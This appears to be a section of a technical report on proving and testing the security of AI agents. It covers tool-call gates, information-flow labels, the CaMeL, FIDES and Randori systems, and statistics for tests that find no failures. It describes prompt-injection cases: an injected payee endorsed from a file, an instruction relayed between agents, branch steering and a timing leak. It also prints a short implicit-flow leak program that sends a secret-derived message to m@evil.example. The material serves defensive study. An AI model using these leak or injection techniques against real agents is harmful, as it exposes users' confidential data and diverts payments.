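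A gate can check a message's recipient directly, but it may have to rely on a classifier's guess about whether a document is confidential. In *Efficient and Sound Probabilistic Verification for AI Agents*, Solko-Breslin, Mudrakarta and colleagues (2026) show how a gate can fail when it turns each guess into yes or no. In their example, an agent is about to send an outside service a text that draws on two earlier messages. A message is confidential if it refers to a certain company, and a classifier gives a 45% chance that the first message does and a 25% chance that the second does. Because the gate uses a cut-off of 50% for each message, it treats both as harmless.

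The relevant figure is the chance that at least one of them is confidential, which depends on how the two are related. If they are independent, it is 1 − 0.55 × 0.75, or about 59%. It falls to 45% if the second is confidential only when the first is, and rises to 70% if they are never both confidential. The gate has no information about which case applies, so the method uses the highest figure, 70%.

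Finding the worst case exactly requires solving an optimisation problem with a variable for every combination of true and false facts, and thirty facts give about a billion combinations. Solko-Breslin and colleagues instead solve a much smaller problem that tracks facts only individually and in pairs. They prove that its answer, R′, is never lower than the true probability of a violation, R. If the gate allows a call only when R′ ≤ τ, every allowed call therefore has R ≤ τ. Because R′ can be higher than R, the gate sometimes blocks calls whose real risk is below τ. On benchmarks for agents that use a command line and other tools, they report that their method balances security and useful work better than earlier methods did.

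The proof relies on probabilities that must be estimated separately. To estimate them, an engineer runs a tool, such as one that redacts personal data, on examples with known answers and calculates an upper limit on its failure rate at a chosen confidence level. The limit is valid only for documents like those examples. Solko-Breslin and colleagues also assume, without testing it, that attackers cannot make the tools fail more often. This assumption is doubtful for an office assistant whose classifier processes emails from strangers.

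The bound also allows violations at a rate of up to τ, so it does not guarantee that no salary will ever reach an outsider.

### The office assistant's rule

The assistant's claim covers pay figures "in any form", which no short program can reliably recognise in a message. Following Schneider, the employer can instead enforce a stricter rule that blocks every message to an unapproved outside address, including any that contains pay figures. In the following pseudocode, APPROVED contains all company addresses and a few outside ones, and only an administrator can edit it.

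```
on call send_message(to, cc, bcc, body, attachments):
    recipients ← all addresses in to, cc and bcc,
                 with mailing lists expanded
    if recipients is empty or any address is unreadable:
        decision ← BLOCK
    else if every recipient is in APPROVED:
        decision ← ALLOW
    else:
        show the user the recipients, body and attachments
        if the user accepts this exact message:
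            decision ← ALLOW, once
        else:
            decision ← BLOCK

on call search_mail or read_file:
    decision ← ALLOW

on any other call:
    decision ← BLOCK

log the call, the rule version and the decision
if decision is ALLOW: execute the call exactly as checked
```

Only two branches allow a message. Checking both proves that every message the gate lets through goes either to approved addresses alone or to recipients whom the user accepted along with that exact text. This holds whatever the model writes, provided that every call passes through the gate, the agent cannot change the gate or the list, and the mail server delivers only to the addresses in the call.

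A check that covered only the `to` field would let the assistant copy in a stranger, and one that did not expand mailing lists would miss an outsider on the list. Allowing the call "once" prevents the agent from reusing an approval, and NOMOS prevents the reuse of confirmations in the same way.

### What the gate leaves open

A list of approved recipients doesn't control what the assistant sends them. If the company's outside lawyer is on the list, an injected instruction can still make the assistant send her the salary file. Yu and colleagues saw this problem in their banking tests, where the agent diverted a payment to someone the user had paid before in 8 of 288 attacked runs. The policy permitted those payments. Shi and colleagues exclude attacks that need only the permissions for the user's own task. Stopping these attacks requires labels that record where the content came from.

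If the assistant also had a shell, which runs any command it receives, a single line could upload the file to a website without calling `send_message`. The pseudocode blocks a shell, but an employer who later wants one has to let some commands through. Schneider warns that a rule against sending works only if its definition of "send" includes every way to send, and some ways may be far from obvious. Progent has this problem when it runs as a proxy between an existing agent product and its outside tools, because it does not check calls to the product's built-in tools. It is safer to leave the shell out, or to run it on a machine with no network connection.

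The proof cannot reveal an error in translating the policy into rules, because it starts from the rules as written. Of the 40 violations that remained in NOMOS's retail test, 21 broke two clauses that the compiler had never turned into rules. Most of the others happened because the rule requiring confirmation did not cover the tool that changes a customer's address.

If users approve every request, the gate still enforces its rule, but the rule protects nobody. Attackers can encourage this by triggering many approval requests, and Zhu and Wang suggest limiting their rate. The employer can also keep requests rare by having the administrator approve regular contacts in advance. In Progent's tests, no attack succeeded when people reviewed the first policy and every expansion of it. But Shi and colleagues assumed that reviewers had strong security awareness and would reject any malicious address,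 so busy office staff will probably do worse.

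## Proving that untrusted data cannot steer the agent

Even with a list of approved recipients, an injected instruction can make the office assistant send the salary file to the company's outside lawyer, who is on the list. Information-flow control can stop this attack. The harness labels each piece of data, updates the labels as the agent combines data, and checks them before a tool acts.

### How labels work

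An integrity label records whether an outsider could have written the data, and a confidentiality label records who may read it. Suppose a user called Ana works with the following data:

| Data | Trusted? | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|
| Ana's request | Yes | Anyone |
| Salary file | Yes | Ana and Ben |
| Project report | Yes | Ana and Carla |
| A stranger's email | No | Anyone |

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, give the usual rule for combining labels. Text that draws on several sources is trusted only if all of them are, and only people who may read every source may read the result. If i is the integrity of the data and R its set of permitted readers, then

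(i₁, R₁) ⊔ (i₂, R₂) = (the less trusted of i₁ and i₂, R₁ ∩ R₂).

A note based on the salary file and the project report is therefore trusted, but only Ana may read it. A note based on the salary file and the stranger's email is untrusted, and only Ana and Ben may read it.

The harness applies two rules before it executes a call. The integrity rule allows an action with consequences, such as a payment, only if the choice of action and its arguments come from trusted data. The readers' rule allows a message only if every recipient is permitted to read everything in it. If the assistant reads a stranger's email and then tries to send the salary file to a lawyer who isn't permitted to read it, the readers' rule blocks the call. Even if the lawyer were permitted to read salaries, the integrity rule would block the call because the model chose it after reading the stranger's email.

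Labeling the model's own output is difficult because nobody can reliably tell which parts of a prompt influenced it. Costa and colleagues therefore give the output the combined label of the whole prompt. This is safe, but once the assistant has opened one email from outside, all its later calls are untrusted and it can't send anything.

### Noninterference

The property that labels aim to guarantee is noninterference: changing the untrusted inputs cannot change what anyone observes at the protected outputs. For the office assistant, the untrusted inputs are emails from outside, and the protected outputs might be the messages it sends. Let A(t, u) be the result of running the agent on trusted inputs t and untrusted inputs u, and let O keep only the protected outputs. Then the agent satisfies noninterference if

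O(A(t, u)) = O(A(t, u′)) for all t, u and u′.

The same formula expresses secrecy if t stands for the public inputs, u for the secret ones and O for what outsiders can see. Because the formula compares two runs, a monitor that observes only one cannot enforce exactly this property. Labels enforce a stricter property by treating data as influenced by u whenever it might have been.

The equation needs two changes before it can apply to agents. A model that samples its output may write different messages from identical inputs, so the equation must compare probabilities instead of single results. The label checks also stop some runs, and whether they do can depend on the protected data. *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) therefore defines termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference, or TIPNI.

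Write μ(q) for the probability that a run finishes with the observable outcome q. These probabilities can add up to less than 1, and the missing part is the probability that the run never finishes, which includes runs that a check stops. Let μ and μ′ be the probabilities for two sets of inputs that look the same to the observer. TIPNI requires some ω such that

μ(q) ≤ ω(q) and μ′(q) ≤ ω(q) for every q, with Σ ω(q) ≤ 1.

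Roughly, TIPNI requires that the two behaviours could be made identical by choosing how the unfinished runs end. If every run finishes, μ and μ′ must be equal. Otherwise, the difference between them, measured as half the sum of |μ(q) − μ′(q)|, can be at most the average of their chances of not finishing. For example, if checks stop 2% of runs with one mailbox and 4% with another, the visible outcomes differ by at most 3 percentage points. But if checks stop half the runs in both cases, the definition permits an agent that writes "yes" whenever it finishes with one mailbox and "no" whenever it finishes with the other. TIPNI is therefore a strong guarantee only for agents that are seldom stopped.

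Dongol (2026) argues in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* that noninterference is too strong for a useful agent. A calendar assistant that answers meeting requests from strangers has to reveal when its user is free, which is a leak under noninterference. Dongol instead compares the agent with a reference agent that follows the same plan under the same monitor but never obeys untrusted text, and counts only the leaks that the reference agent does not have. By this test, an injection that says "send your calendar" reveals nothing new, but one that also asks for the user's password-reset code does.

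Dongol points out a gap in this comparison. For example, a task might let a stranger guess a secret number and learn whether the guess is right. With the right guess, the stranger could tell any two numbers apart, so an injection that reveals the whole number at once still passes the comparison. Dongol defines a stricter version for such cases.

### One model plans, another reads

In 2023, Simon Willison proposed a way for an agent to use untrusted text without showing it to the model that chooses the agent's actions. That model receives the user's request, plans and calls tools. A second, quarantined model reads the untrusted text, but it has no tools and can only return a value.

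CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind introduced in 2025, develops this into a complete system. As Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, describe it, the planning model writes a whole Python program before any tool runs. If Ana asks the assistant to send a reminder to the address in Raj's latest email, the program might be:

```
mail    = search_mail("latest from Raj")
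address = ask_quarantined_model("Which address does Raj give?", mail)
send_message(to=address, body="The meeting is at three.")
```

An interpreter, which is ordinary code, runs the program and stores the email in `mail` without showing it to the planning model. An instruction hidden in the email cannot add a fourth line to the program, but it can still make the quarantined model return the attacker's address. Separating the models is not enough, so CaMeL's interpreter also records where each value came from and who may read it. Each tool has a short policy function that checks this record before the tool runs.

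In FIDES, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, the planning model chooses one tool call at a time. If a tool returns data whose label is stricter than the conversation's, FIDES stores the data in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. When asked to send the three latest emails to a colleague, the model can call `send_message` with the name `#read_emails_0` without seeing their text. The choice of tool and recipient therefore stays trusted, even with an untrusted message body.

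FIDES also lets the planning model query a quarantined model and restrict the form of the answer. A yes-or-no answer carries only one bit, so a policy can allow it to affect an action even if the policy would block free text. This makes more tasks possible, but an attacker may need to control only that one bit if it determines whether the agent sends a payment.

Both groups tested their systems on AgentDojo, which has 97 user tasks and 35 attacker goals. Pairing each task with each goal in the same setting gives 949 attacked tasks. Costa and colleagues report that, with appropriate policies, FIDES stopped every injection in the benchmark, but Garby and colleagues note that the evaluation excludes two injections as outside the scope of those policies. With the checks on, FIDES completed 8% more tasks than a basic planner when both used GPT-4o, and 16% more with o1. With the checks off, its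 extra machinery reduced completion by 6.3%. Both models are old, so these figures are a poor guide to completion rates today.

*Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025) cites an early completion rate of 67% for CaMeL. Garby and colleagues made more recent measurements when they reran CaMeL on the banking tasks, after finding two ways it can leak secrets.

### Two leaks in CaMeL

CaMeL blocks the obvious way to leak a fact about a salary, which is to send a message only if the salary exceeds some amount. The interpreter notices that a secret controls whether the message goes out. The following program, which works in the way Garby and colleagues describe, gets around this:

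```
low  = True
rich = True
if salary > 100000:
    low = False
if low:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_message("m@evil.example", "rich")
```

CaMeL marks a variable as secret when the program changes it under a secret condition. But it does so only on the branch that runs, so the variable keeps its old label if the program skips the change.

| Lines | Salary above 100,000 | Salary of 100,000 or less |
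|---|---|---|
| `if salary > 100000: low = False` | Runs, so `low` is False and secret | Skipped, so `low` stays True and public |
| `if low: rich = False` | Skipped, so `rich` stays True and public | Runs, so `rich` is False and public |
| `if rich: send_message(...)` | The condition is public, so CaMeL sends the message | No message |

The attacker receives a message exactly when the salary is above 100,000, although `rich` is public in both cases. The trick dates from the 1970s. A tracker that monitors only the lines that run can't record the information revealed when the program skips a line.

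The standard remedy is to stop the program when it tries to change a public variable under a secret condition, here at `low = False`. Stopping can reveal one bit, since someone may notice it. TIPNI permits this kind of leak.

That single bit matters because CaMeL has another leak, through retries. When a program fails, an ordinary Python loop outside the interpreter calls the planning model for another attempt, which starts without the labels from the previous one. Whether the policy blocked an attempt can depend on a secret, and the next attempt can depend on whether it was blocked. A series of attempts can therefore test whether the salary is above 500,000, then above 250,000, and so on. Twenty such tests are enough to find a salary of up to about a million to the nearest dollar. CaMeL censors the error messages it passes on, but nobody has proved that this closes the leak.

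An attacker would struggle to exploit either leak through an email alone, because CaMeL's planning model writes the program without reading the email. But the planning model treats the user's request as trusted, and Tallam and Miller warn that phishing can get an attacker's wording into that request. The leaks also show that hand-written tracking is easy to get wrong. For instance, Garby and colleagues found that inserting an untrusted value into a piece of text made the value trusted.

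Costa and colleagues prove only explicit secrecy for FIDES, which covers the direct copying of secrets but not what an observer learns from which calls the agent makes. They argue that full noninterference would essentially forbid the agent to use any tool with publicly visible effects after it had used one that might read a secret.

### A theorem about every program

Garby and colleagues designed LLMbda to prove TIPNI for agents in general. LLMbda is a small programming language in which a program can prompt a model, copy or clear the conversation, and run code that the model writes. Every value has a label, and so does the conversation. Code that the model writes runs under the label of the conversation that produced it, so a model that has read untrusted text cannot write code whose results count as trusted.

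Their main theorem states that every LLMbda program satisfies TIPNI, including programs that generate further programs. The proof uses an imaginary second interpreter, which skips any computation as soon as its label shows that the observer may not see it, and returns a blank value. Three facts then give the result:

1. For each visible outcome, the skipping interpreter is at least as likely to finish with that outcome as the real one.
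2. It never uses the hidden data, so it gives the same probabilities for any two inputs that look alike to the observer.
3. Those probabilities add up to at most 1.

They are therefore the ω that the definition requires.

The proof is written in Lean, which checks every step by computer. The interpreter that runs the agents is also a Lean program, and another theorem shows that it behaves as the mathematical description requires. The proof and the experiments therefore concern the same program, unlike those in PACE. The proof does not cover the code that contacts the language model over the network. It treats the model's replies as random draws whose probabilities depend only on the conversation so far.

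Noninterference would make some ordinary requests impossible. If Ana asks the assistant to find a friend's bank details on the friend's website and send $50, untrusted data has to determine where the money goes. LLMbda therefore has an operation called `endorse`, which marks an untrusted value as trusted. A second theorem shows that, however a program uses `endorse`, secrets still cannot affect what outsiders see, except through whether the run finishes. The theorem does not guarantee that endorsed data cannot affect the agent's other actions.

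### The two attacks that succeeded

Garby and colleagues used LLMbda to write an agent called Randori and tested it on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks. Randori first practises on an invented bank account, where it can correct errors in its program without touching real data, and then runs the finished program on the real account. This replaces CaMeL's leaky retry loop. The researchers paired each task with each of nine attacks and ran each pair three times on each of three models, for 1,296 attacked runs. They also reran CaMeL with two of the models, although some of its attacked runs did not finish.

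| System | Model | Tasks completed without an attack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | GPT-5.2 | 75.0% | 2 of 432 |
| Randori | Qwen3.7-plus | 75.0% | 0 of 432 |
| Randori | MiMo-v2.5 | 64.6% | 0 of 432 |
| CaMeL, policies off | GPT-5.2 | 66.7% | 1 of 240 |
| CaMeL, policies off | MiMo-v2.5 | 70.8% | 4 of 382 |
| CaMeL, policies on | GPT-5.2 | 37.5% | 0 of 231 |
| CaMeL, policies on | MiMo-v2.5 | 37.5% | 0 of 357 |

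Both successful attacks on Randori used the same user task and the same injected request. The user asked the agent to read a text file and make the payment it described, and the attack replaced the file's contents with a request to pay the attacker. GPT-5.2 had written a program that endorsed the file's contents, so the payment tool's check accepted them.

The theorems did not rule out this attack. The guarantee that untrusted data cannot affect trusted actions covers only programs without `endorse`. The guarantee that still holds with `endorse` is about secrets, and none leaked. Labels record where text came from, and the attacker's text came from the file the user had told the agent to obey. Without `endorse`, Randori blocks the attack, but it also can't do the task when the file is genuine. Removing `endorse` lowered task completion from 75.0% to 62.5% with Qwen3.7-plus and from 64.6%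 to 54.2% with MiMo-v2.5.

CaMeL's published evaluation also contains a successful attack of this kind, which its developers place outside their threat model. An employer can avoid the problem by not letting the assistant take payment instructions from files that outsiders can change, or by having a person confirm the payee.

The labels achieved less than the low number of successful attacks suggests. In 97 of the 144 combinations, the attack needed an action that a program written for the user's task would not normally contain, such as a payment when the user had asked only for a summary. Planning before reading untrusted data is usually enough to defeat these attacks, even without the labels. Only the other 47 combinations, or 423 of Randori's runs, really tested the labels.

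Even planning first can fail if the plan is too general. Two of the five attacks that succeeded against CaMeL when it ran without policies exploited a task that told the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The planning model wrote a loop that could use any of the tools to carry out whatever instruction the file contained, so the attacker could again steer the agent.

Randori completed about twice as many tasks as CaMeL did with its policies on, but part of that gap comes from looser rules, because Randori enforces only some of CaMeL's policies and may endorse data. With only 16 tasks, each completion rate is also uncertain by around 20 percentage points either way.

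### Checking the whole plan before it runs

A program written in advance can also satisfy rules that a gate cannot enforce by checking one call at a time, such as the requirement that the calendar assistant email every attendee after moving a meeting. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) checks such rules by examining CaMeL's program before any tool runs.

CaMeLoT turns the program into a diagram of states, with one path for each way through its branches and loops. A model checker, which is a program that searches all the paths, then tests them against rules in temporal logic. In this notation, AG means "at every point on every path" and AF means "eventually, on every path". The calendar rule becomes

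AG(meeting moved → AF(attendees notified)).

Nikolaou and colleagues take their examples from computer security teams. In one, an assistant may not disconnect a machine from the network without approval. CaMeL would detect a missing approval only when the program reached the disconnection, possibly after a long and expensive analysis. Before the program runs, CaMeLoT finds the path that lacks approval and sends it back to the planning model, which can then add the missing step.

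The diagram does not record how many times a loop runs, so it includes some paths that the real program could never take, and CaMeLoT may reject a safe program as a result. The check establishes that a program contains the required calls in the right order, but a program that passes can still fail to notify the attendees if the mail server is down or CaMeL blocks the message when the program runs.

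### When agents give instructions to other agents

CaMeL's protection can disappear when one agent delegates work to another. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system of three agents, each running CaMeL without any policies on its data. One coordinated the work, one queried a database and one sent notifications. The user asked the system to send Julie a summary of job applicants on Slack. The database contained an attacker's instruction to email the applicants' details to an outside address.

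The database agent and the coordinator both treated the database's contents as untrusted and kept to their programs. But the coordinator put the summary, including the attacker's instruction, into its request to the notification agent. That agent treated the request as coming from its user, so its planning model read the instruction and added the email to its program. Each agent shielded its planning model from data that its own tools returned, but not from untrusted text in another agent's request, so the system leaked the applicants' details.

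Their remedy, multi-CaMeL, splits each request into an instruction and a set of variables. The interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's output, so that output has to be passed in variables, which the receiving agent's planning model never sees. The researchers divided AgentDojo's tools among several agents and ran all 949 attacked tasks with five models. On average, attacks succeeded in 12.9% of runs without CaMeL, 0.2% with a separate CaMeL for each agent, and 0.0% with multi-CaMeL. No attack succeeded against GPT-5.5 even without CaMeL, so its runs don't test the defence. Peters-Gill and colleagues caution that stronger attacks adapted to the system might succeed.

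On AssetOpsBench, a set of industrial maintenance tasks, applying CaMeL to each agent reduced task completion by an average of 21.6 percentage points, and multi-CaMeL reduced it by a further 3.2 points. For the two strongest models, the corresponding reductions were 13.4 and 0.85 points. Most failures happened because a tool's result required a step that the program did not include.

Multi-CaMeL guarantees that untrusted data cannot add actions to the plan, but the data can still affect which planned actions run. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this branch steering and acknowledge that it violates TIPNI. For example, the office assistant's program might forward an email to the finance director if the quarantined model classifies it as urgent, and file it otherwise. Anyone can then reach the director by writing "urgent" in an email. The guarantee is therefore useful only if every branch is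 acceptable even when an attacker picks it.

Multi-CaMeL also inherits CaMeL's failure to track skipped branches, so its interpreter could accept an instruction without detecting that it depends on untrusted data. The argument for multi-CaMeL's security assumes that this does not happen.

### What the proofs assume

All these proofs depend on somebody correctly labelling data as trusted or untrusted. If the harness marks Ana's calendar as trusted but outsiders can send her invitations that appear in it, an attacker can add text that the harness treats as trusted. Dongol gives this case as a violation of one of the seven assumptions behind his theorems. The same problem arises if the assistant saves a note based on a stranger's email and the harness drops the untrusted label when the assistant later retrieves the note.

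The policy also has to forbid the right things. A proof that the assistant never sends data to someone without permission to read it does not protect the salary file if that file's list of readers includes everyone. CaMeL needs a policy function for each tool, so its guarantee depends on many separate pieces of code. *SPA* (2026) makes this point about systems with richer policies in general, because they have no single rule that covers all data flows. Tallam and Miller expect companies with hundreds of tools to end up with inconsistent and duplicated rules.

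The description of each tool has to match what the tool does. FIDES works out the label of a tool's result from a list of the data the tool may read and change. If `send_message` also fetches a preview of every link in a message, and the list omits this, the fetch can send secrets to the linked website unchecked. Garby and colleagues proved their theorem for programs that contain all their data sources. Randori's bank was therefore a simulation written in LLMbda. Garby and colleagues name the lack of a better model of outside tools as a limitation.

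The mathematics also leaves out some of what an attacker can observe, such as timing. Dongol shows that this matters even for a gate that lets a user approve one exact message, once. Suppose Ana approves a reply, and an injected instruction tells the agent to send her private code. The gate blocks the code unless it matches the approved reply. In that case the reply goes out one step early, and an attacker who can observe the timing learns what the code is.

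Finally, every tool call and every piece of untrusted text must pass through the interpreter or monitor. AgentDojo's harness meets this condition because it executes every call itself. An assistant with a web browser that the interpreter does not control does not meet it, because unlabeled text from a page can enter the model's prompt and the browser can send data out unchecked.

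## What a test without failures shows

Proofs about a gate or an interpreter do not show how often the model attempts a forbidden action, so testers still have to run the agent. The claim about the office assistant is that it attempts to send out pay data in fewer than 1 in 1,000 runs. If testers run the assistant many times and see no attempt, they can calculate how high the rate could still be.

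### The rule of three

Suppose every run has the same chance p of a forbidden action, independently of the other runs. One run is then clean with probability 1 − p, and n runs are all clean with probability (1 − p)ⁿ. The higher the rate, the less likely a clean result is. The 95% upper bound is the rate at which a clean result would have a probability of only 5%:

(1 − p)ⁿ = 0.05, so p = 1 − 0.05^(1/n).

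Taking logarithms gives n ln(1 − p) = ln 0.05 ≈ −3. Since ln(1 − p) is close to −p when p is small, the bound is about 3/n.

Hanley and Lippman-Hand published this approximation in 1983 as the rule of three. In *Probability of adverse events that have not yet occurred* (1995), Eypasch, Lefering and colleagues applied it to published series of keyhole operations on the appendix and gallbladder. No series had reported a major blood vessel injury that led to death or the loss of a limb, but the upper bound on the risk still ranged from 0.4% to 12% across the series.

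For the office assistant, 2,995 clean runs put the bound just under 1 in 1,000. A service that handles 100,000 tasks a day could fail about 100 times a day at that rate. The office assistant handles about 4,000 requests a day, or a million in a working year. Testers would need about three million clean runs to show with the same confidence that it makes no more than one attempt a year.

A different confidence level changes only the 0.05 in the calculation. *CORE-RL* (2026), which tests control programs that learn by trial and error, calculates that 45 clean episodes are enough to bound the failure rate at 5% with 90% confidence. If the assistant makes one attempt during the test, testers need about 4,700 runs instead of 2,995 to establish the same bound of 1 in 1,000 at 95% confidence.

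If a system's failure rate is above the 95% bound, the chance that a test of this size finds no failures is at most 5%. This does not mean that the true rate has a 95% chance of being below the bound, and the bound is not an estimate of the rate. As *Sound Probabilistic Safety Bounds for Large Language Models* (2026) points out, the matching lower bound is zero when a sample contains no harmful outputs, so a test without failures does not distinguish a system that rarely fails from one that never does.

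Using the bound as an estimate can distort later calculations. In *The Role of Informative Priors in Zero Numerator Problems*, Winkler, Smith and Fryback (2002) warn that a 95% bound chosen out of caution may backfire in this way, and *Estimating Risk when Zero Events have been Observed* adds that combining several bounds makes the result even more pessimistic. Suppose testers run each of ten tools 300 times without a failure. Each tool's bound is about 1%, so adding the bounds gives 10% for a task that uses every tool once. The right bound on the total is 1%, because if the ten rates added up to more than that, all 3,000 runs would be clean less than 5% of the time.

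The usual formula for a margin of error is based on the observed failure rate, so a test without failures gives a margin of zero, which wrongly implies that the agent is certain never to fail. *Don't Use the CLT in LLM Evals* (2025) advises against such formulas for tests with fewer than a few hundred data points.

### How much a clean result should change the odds

An employer deciding whether to install the assistant wants to know whether it is acceptable or unsafe. Kaur's approach is to compare how likely a clean result would be in each case. Let q₁ be the chance that one trial finds a failure in an unsafe system, and q₀ the chance that it finds one in an acceptable system. The likelihood ratio of n clean trials is

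Λ = [(1 − q₁)/(1 − q₀)]ⁿ.

The new odds that the system is unsafe are the earlier odds multiplied by the ratio Λ. A Λ of 1 leaves the odds unchanged, and a Λ near 0 is strong evidence that the system is acceptable.

For example, suppose the employer thinks the assistant's failure rate is equally likely to be 1 in 100 runs, which would be unsafe, or 1 in 200, which would be acceptable. After 520 clean runs, Λ is (0.99/0.995)⁵²⁰, or about 0.07, and the probability that the assistant is unsafe falls from 50% to 7%. If the two rates are instead 1 in 1,000 and 1 in 2,000, Λ is 0.77 after 520 clean runs, and the probability falls only to 44%.

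Kaur calculates how many clean trials testers need for various purposes. The first two rows below assume, as in the example, that an acceptable system fails half as often as an unsafe one.

| Purpose of the test | Unsafe rate: 1 in 100 | 1 in 1,000 | 1 in 10,000 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Halve the odds that the system is unsafe | 138 | 1,386 | 13,862 |
| Cut those odds to a tenth | 458 | 4,602 | 46,049 |
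| Give an unsafe system less than a 5% chance of a clean result | 299 | 2,995 | 29,956 |

A few hundred trials without a failure provide almost no evidence that rare failures are absent. A system that fails on average once in 10,000 trials has a 95% chance of passing a 520-trial test. If testers can run at most 100,000 trials, a clean result cannot halve the odds that the system is unsafe when an unsafe system would fail less than about once in 72,000 trials.

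Developers do encounter failures this rare. Anthropic's system card for Claude Opus 5 reports that monitoring of internal use found attempts to get around safety classifiers or network restrictions in less than 0.01% of the model's completions. Anthropic's automated audit used about 3,200 sessions per model. A session can contain many completions, so the two numbers are not directly comparable, but an audit of that size would have a 73% chance of missing a fault that appeared in 1 in 10,000 sessions.

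Kaur's paper is a single-author preprint from a company, APIsec Research Labs. The mathematics is elementary, as Kaur acknowledges, and anyone can check the table with a calculator. But the failure rates are assumptions, and nobody knows which column a real assistant belongs in. The sample sizes also depend on how much better the acceptable system is. If it never failed, 230 clean trials would be enough in the first column, instead of 458. The change in the odds needed depends on how much harm a wrong decision would do.

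Kaur finds that, at an unsafe rate of 1 in 100, a clean result on 520 prompts carries 1.4 times as much evidence as a single failure. Both outcomes are evidence that the system is acceptable, because an unsafe system would fail about five times in 520 trials and an acceptable one two or three times. The comparison therefore does not show that a clean result could outweigh a failure that counted against the system. This reasoning does not apply to deliveries of pay data, since the office assistant's claim allows no such deliveries.

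### What counts as one trial

These formulas assume independent trials, which testers can easily overcount. Kaur gives an example from the report on Claude 2, an older Anthropic model. Anthropic counted four harmful cases among 328 prompts, but the model had answered each prompt five times, giving 1,640 responses. One of the four prompts disrupted the model in about half of its responses. Because the report does not give the number of harmful responses, readers can work out the rate per prompt but not the rate per response, which is closer to what users experience.

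Related trials provide less information than independent ones. Testers might write 120 scenarios for the office assistant and make 25 variants of each by changing names and wording, for a total of 3,000 runs. If the assistant handles one variant safely, it will probably handle the others safely too. Let m be the number of runs per scenario, and ρ the correlation between runs of the same scenario, which is 0 if they are unrelated and 1 if they always agree. The usual correction is to divide the number of runs by the design effect,

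1 + (m − 1)ρ.

With m = 25 and ρ = 0.1, the design effect is 3.4. The 3,000 runs are then equivalent to about 882 independent ones, and the upper bound rises from 1 in 1,000 to about 1 in 300.

This correction is rough, because the design effect describes how much an average varies, not the probability of seeing no failures. Kaur prefers a beta-binomial model, which gives each scenario its own failure rate. With the same numbers, that model gives a bound of about 1 in 500, still twice the bound for independent runs.

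Correlations in real evaluations can be much higher than 0.1:

- *DiagnosticIQ* (2026) tests models on industrial maintenance, with about 45 questions for each underlying rule. The correlation within a rule was about 0.9, so the whole benchmark was worth only about 130 independent questions, a fortieth of its actual number.
- *Who Gets Named* (2026), a study of which people language models name in their answers, collected 20 responses to each prompt. The correlation was 0.258, and its 2,400 responses were worth 407.
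- *GYROval* (2026) ran 225 short scenarios about cultural values 30 times each, at a setting that makes a model's output almost the same every time. Counting all 6,750 runs as independent would have made the margin of error about 5.5 times too small.

None of these studies measured forbidden actions, so their correlations may not apply to the office assistant. Its testers also cannot estimate ρ from a test without failures, because they have no failures to correlate. They have to assume a cautious value for ρ or measure it on a system that does fail.

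Running the same scenarios more often does not solve the problem. *How Many Human Judgments Are Enough?* (2026) derives from the design-effect formula that a group of related observations is never worth more than 1/ρ independent ones. With ρ = 0.1, each scenario is worth at most ten independent runs, and 120 scenarios are worth at most 1,200. Testers who want a bound on the overall failure rate should therefore draw a new scenario for every run. Repeated runs are useful for estimating how often one particular email leads to the forbidden action.

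### Attacks that build on one another

If an attacker uses the result of each attempt to plan the next, the attempts are not separate trials. Kaur counts a hundred such attempts by one expert as a single trial, or campaign. A second trial would need a different attacker or random seed, with nothing carried over from the first. Counting the attempts separately would make the sample look a hundred times larger than it is.

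Anthropic tested Claude Opus 4.5 in a web browser against an adaptive attacker that had 100 attempts in each environment. With improved safeguards, 1.4% of attempts succeeded. Anthropic bases each rate it gives for its models on about 2,200 to 3,200 attempts, so 1.4% is about 30 to 45 successes. If the attacker used all 100 attempts in each environment, there were only about 22 to 32 environments. An employer would want to know whether the attacker succeeded once or twice in every environment or dozens of times in one and never in the others, but the 1.4% rate is consistent with both.

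Schneier (2026), in *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection*, gives success rates for one attempt and for fifteen. A single attempt against GPT-5.6 Sol succeeded 3.1% of the time, and at least one attempt in fifteen succeeded 20.0% of the time. If the attempts had been independent, the fifteen-attempt rate would have been about 38%. Presumably nearly all attempts fail on some test cases and many succeed on others, so it would be wrong to calculate the risk from a persistent attacker as if each attempt were independent.

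In *What happens when you put an AI agent's email on Hacker News*, Irarrázaval (2026) describes a public challenge to make his AI assistant leak a secret by emailing it. About 2,000 people took part, and Willison (2026) reports that none of their 6,000 attempts succeeded. If each attempt counts as a trial, the upper bound on the success rate is 1 in 2,000. If each person counts as one, it is about 1 in 670. If participants read about one another's attempts, the trials were not independent and the effective sample is smaller still.

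Neither bound applies to attackers who differ from the participants. Irarrázaval thinks a patient attacker who exchanges 20 emails with the assistant is more dangerous than someone who sends 20 variations at once. The result impressed Willison, but he still advises against using such an agent where a successful injection could do irreversible damage.

### Positive controls

A clean result is no evidence that a fault is absent if the test could not have found it. Testers can check whether the test can find the fault by running it on a positive control, a system that they know has the fault. The share of trials that expose the fault estimates q₁.

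Kaur illustrates the value of a good test with invented numbers. Suppose a campaign of attacks succeeds against an unsafe system 90% of the time and against an acceptable one 10% of the time. If a campaign is unsuccessful, the likelihood ratio is 0.1/0.9, so the odds that the system is unsafe fall to a ninth of what they were. If the unsafe system failed on 1 in 1,000 prompts and the acceptable one on 1 in 2,000, testers using a fixed list of prompts would need about 4,400 clean trials to lower the odds by the same amount.

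If the campaign instead succeeds 90% of the time against both unsafe and acceptable systems, the ratio is 0.1/0.1 = 1, and a failed campaign does not change the odds. A test of the office assistant would have this defect if it counted every outgoing message containing a number as a leak of pay data. Safe and unsafe assistants would both "leak" in most runs, and a run without a leak would show only that the assistant had no reason to write a number. The evidence is also weak when the two success rates are close but not equal. If the campaign succeeds 90% of the time against unsafe systems and 85% against acceptable ones, five failed campaigns in a row are weaker evidence than one failed campaign in the first example.

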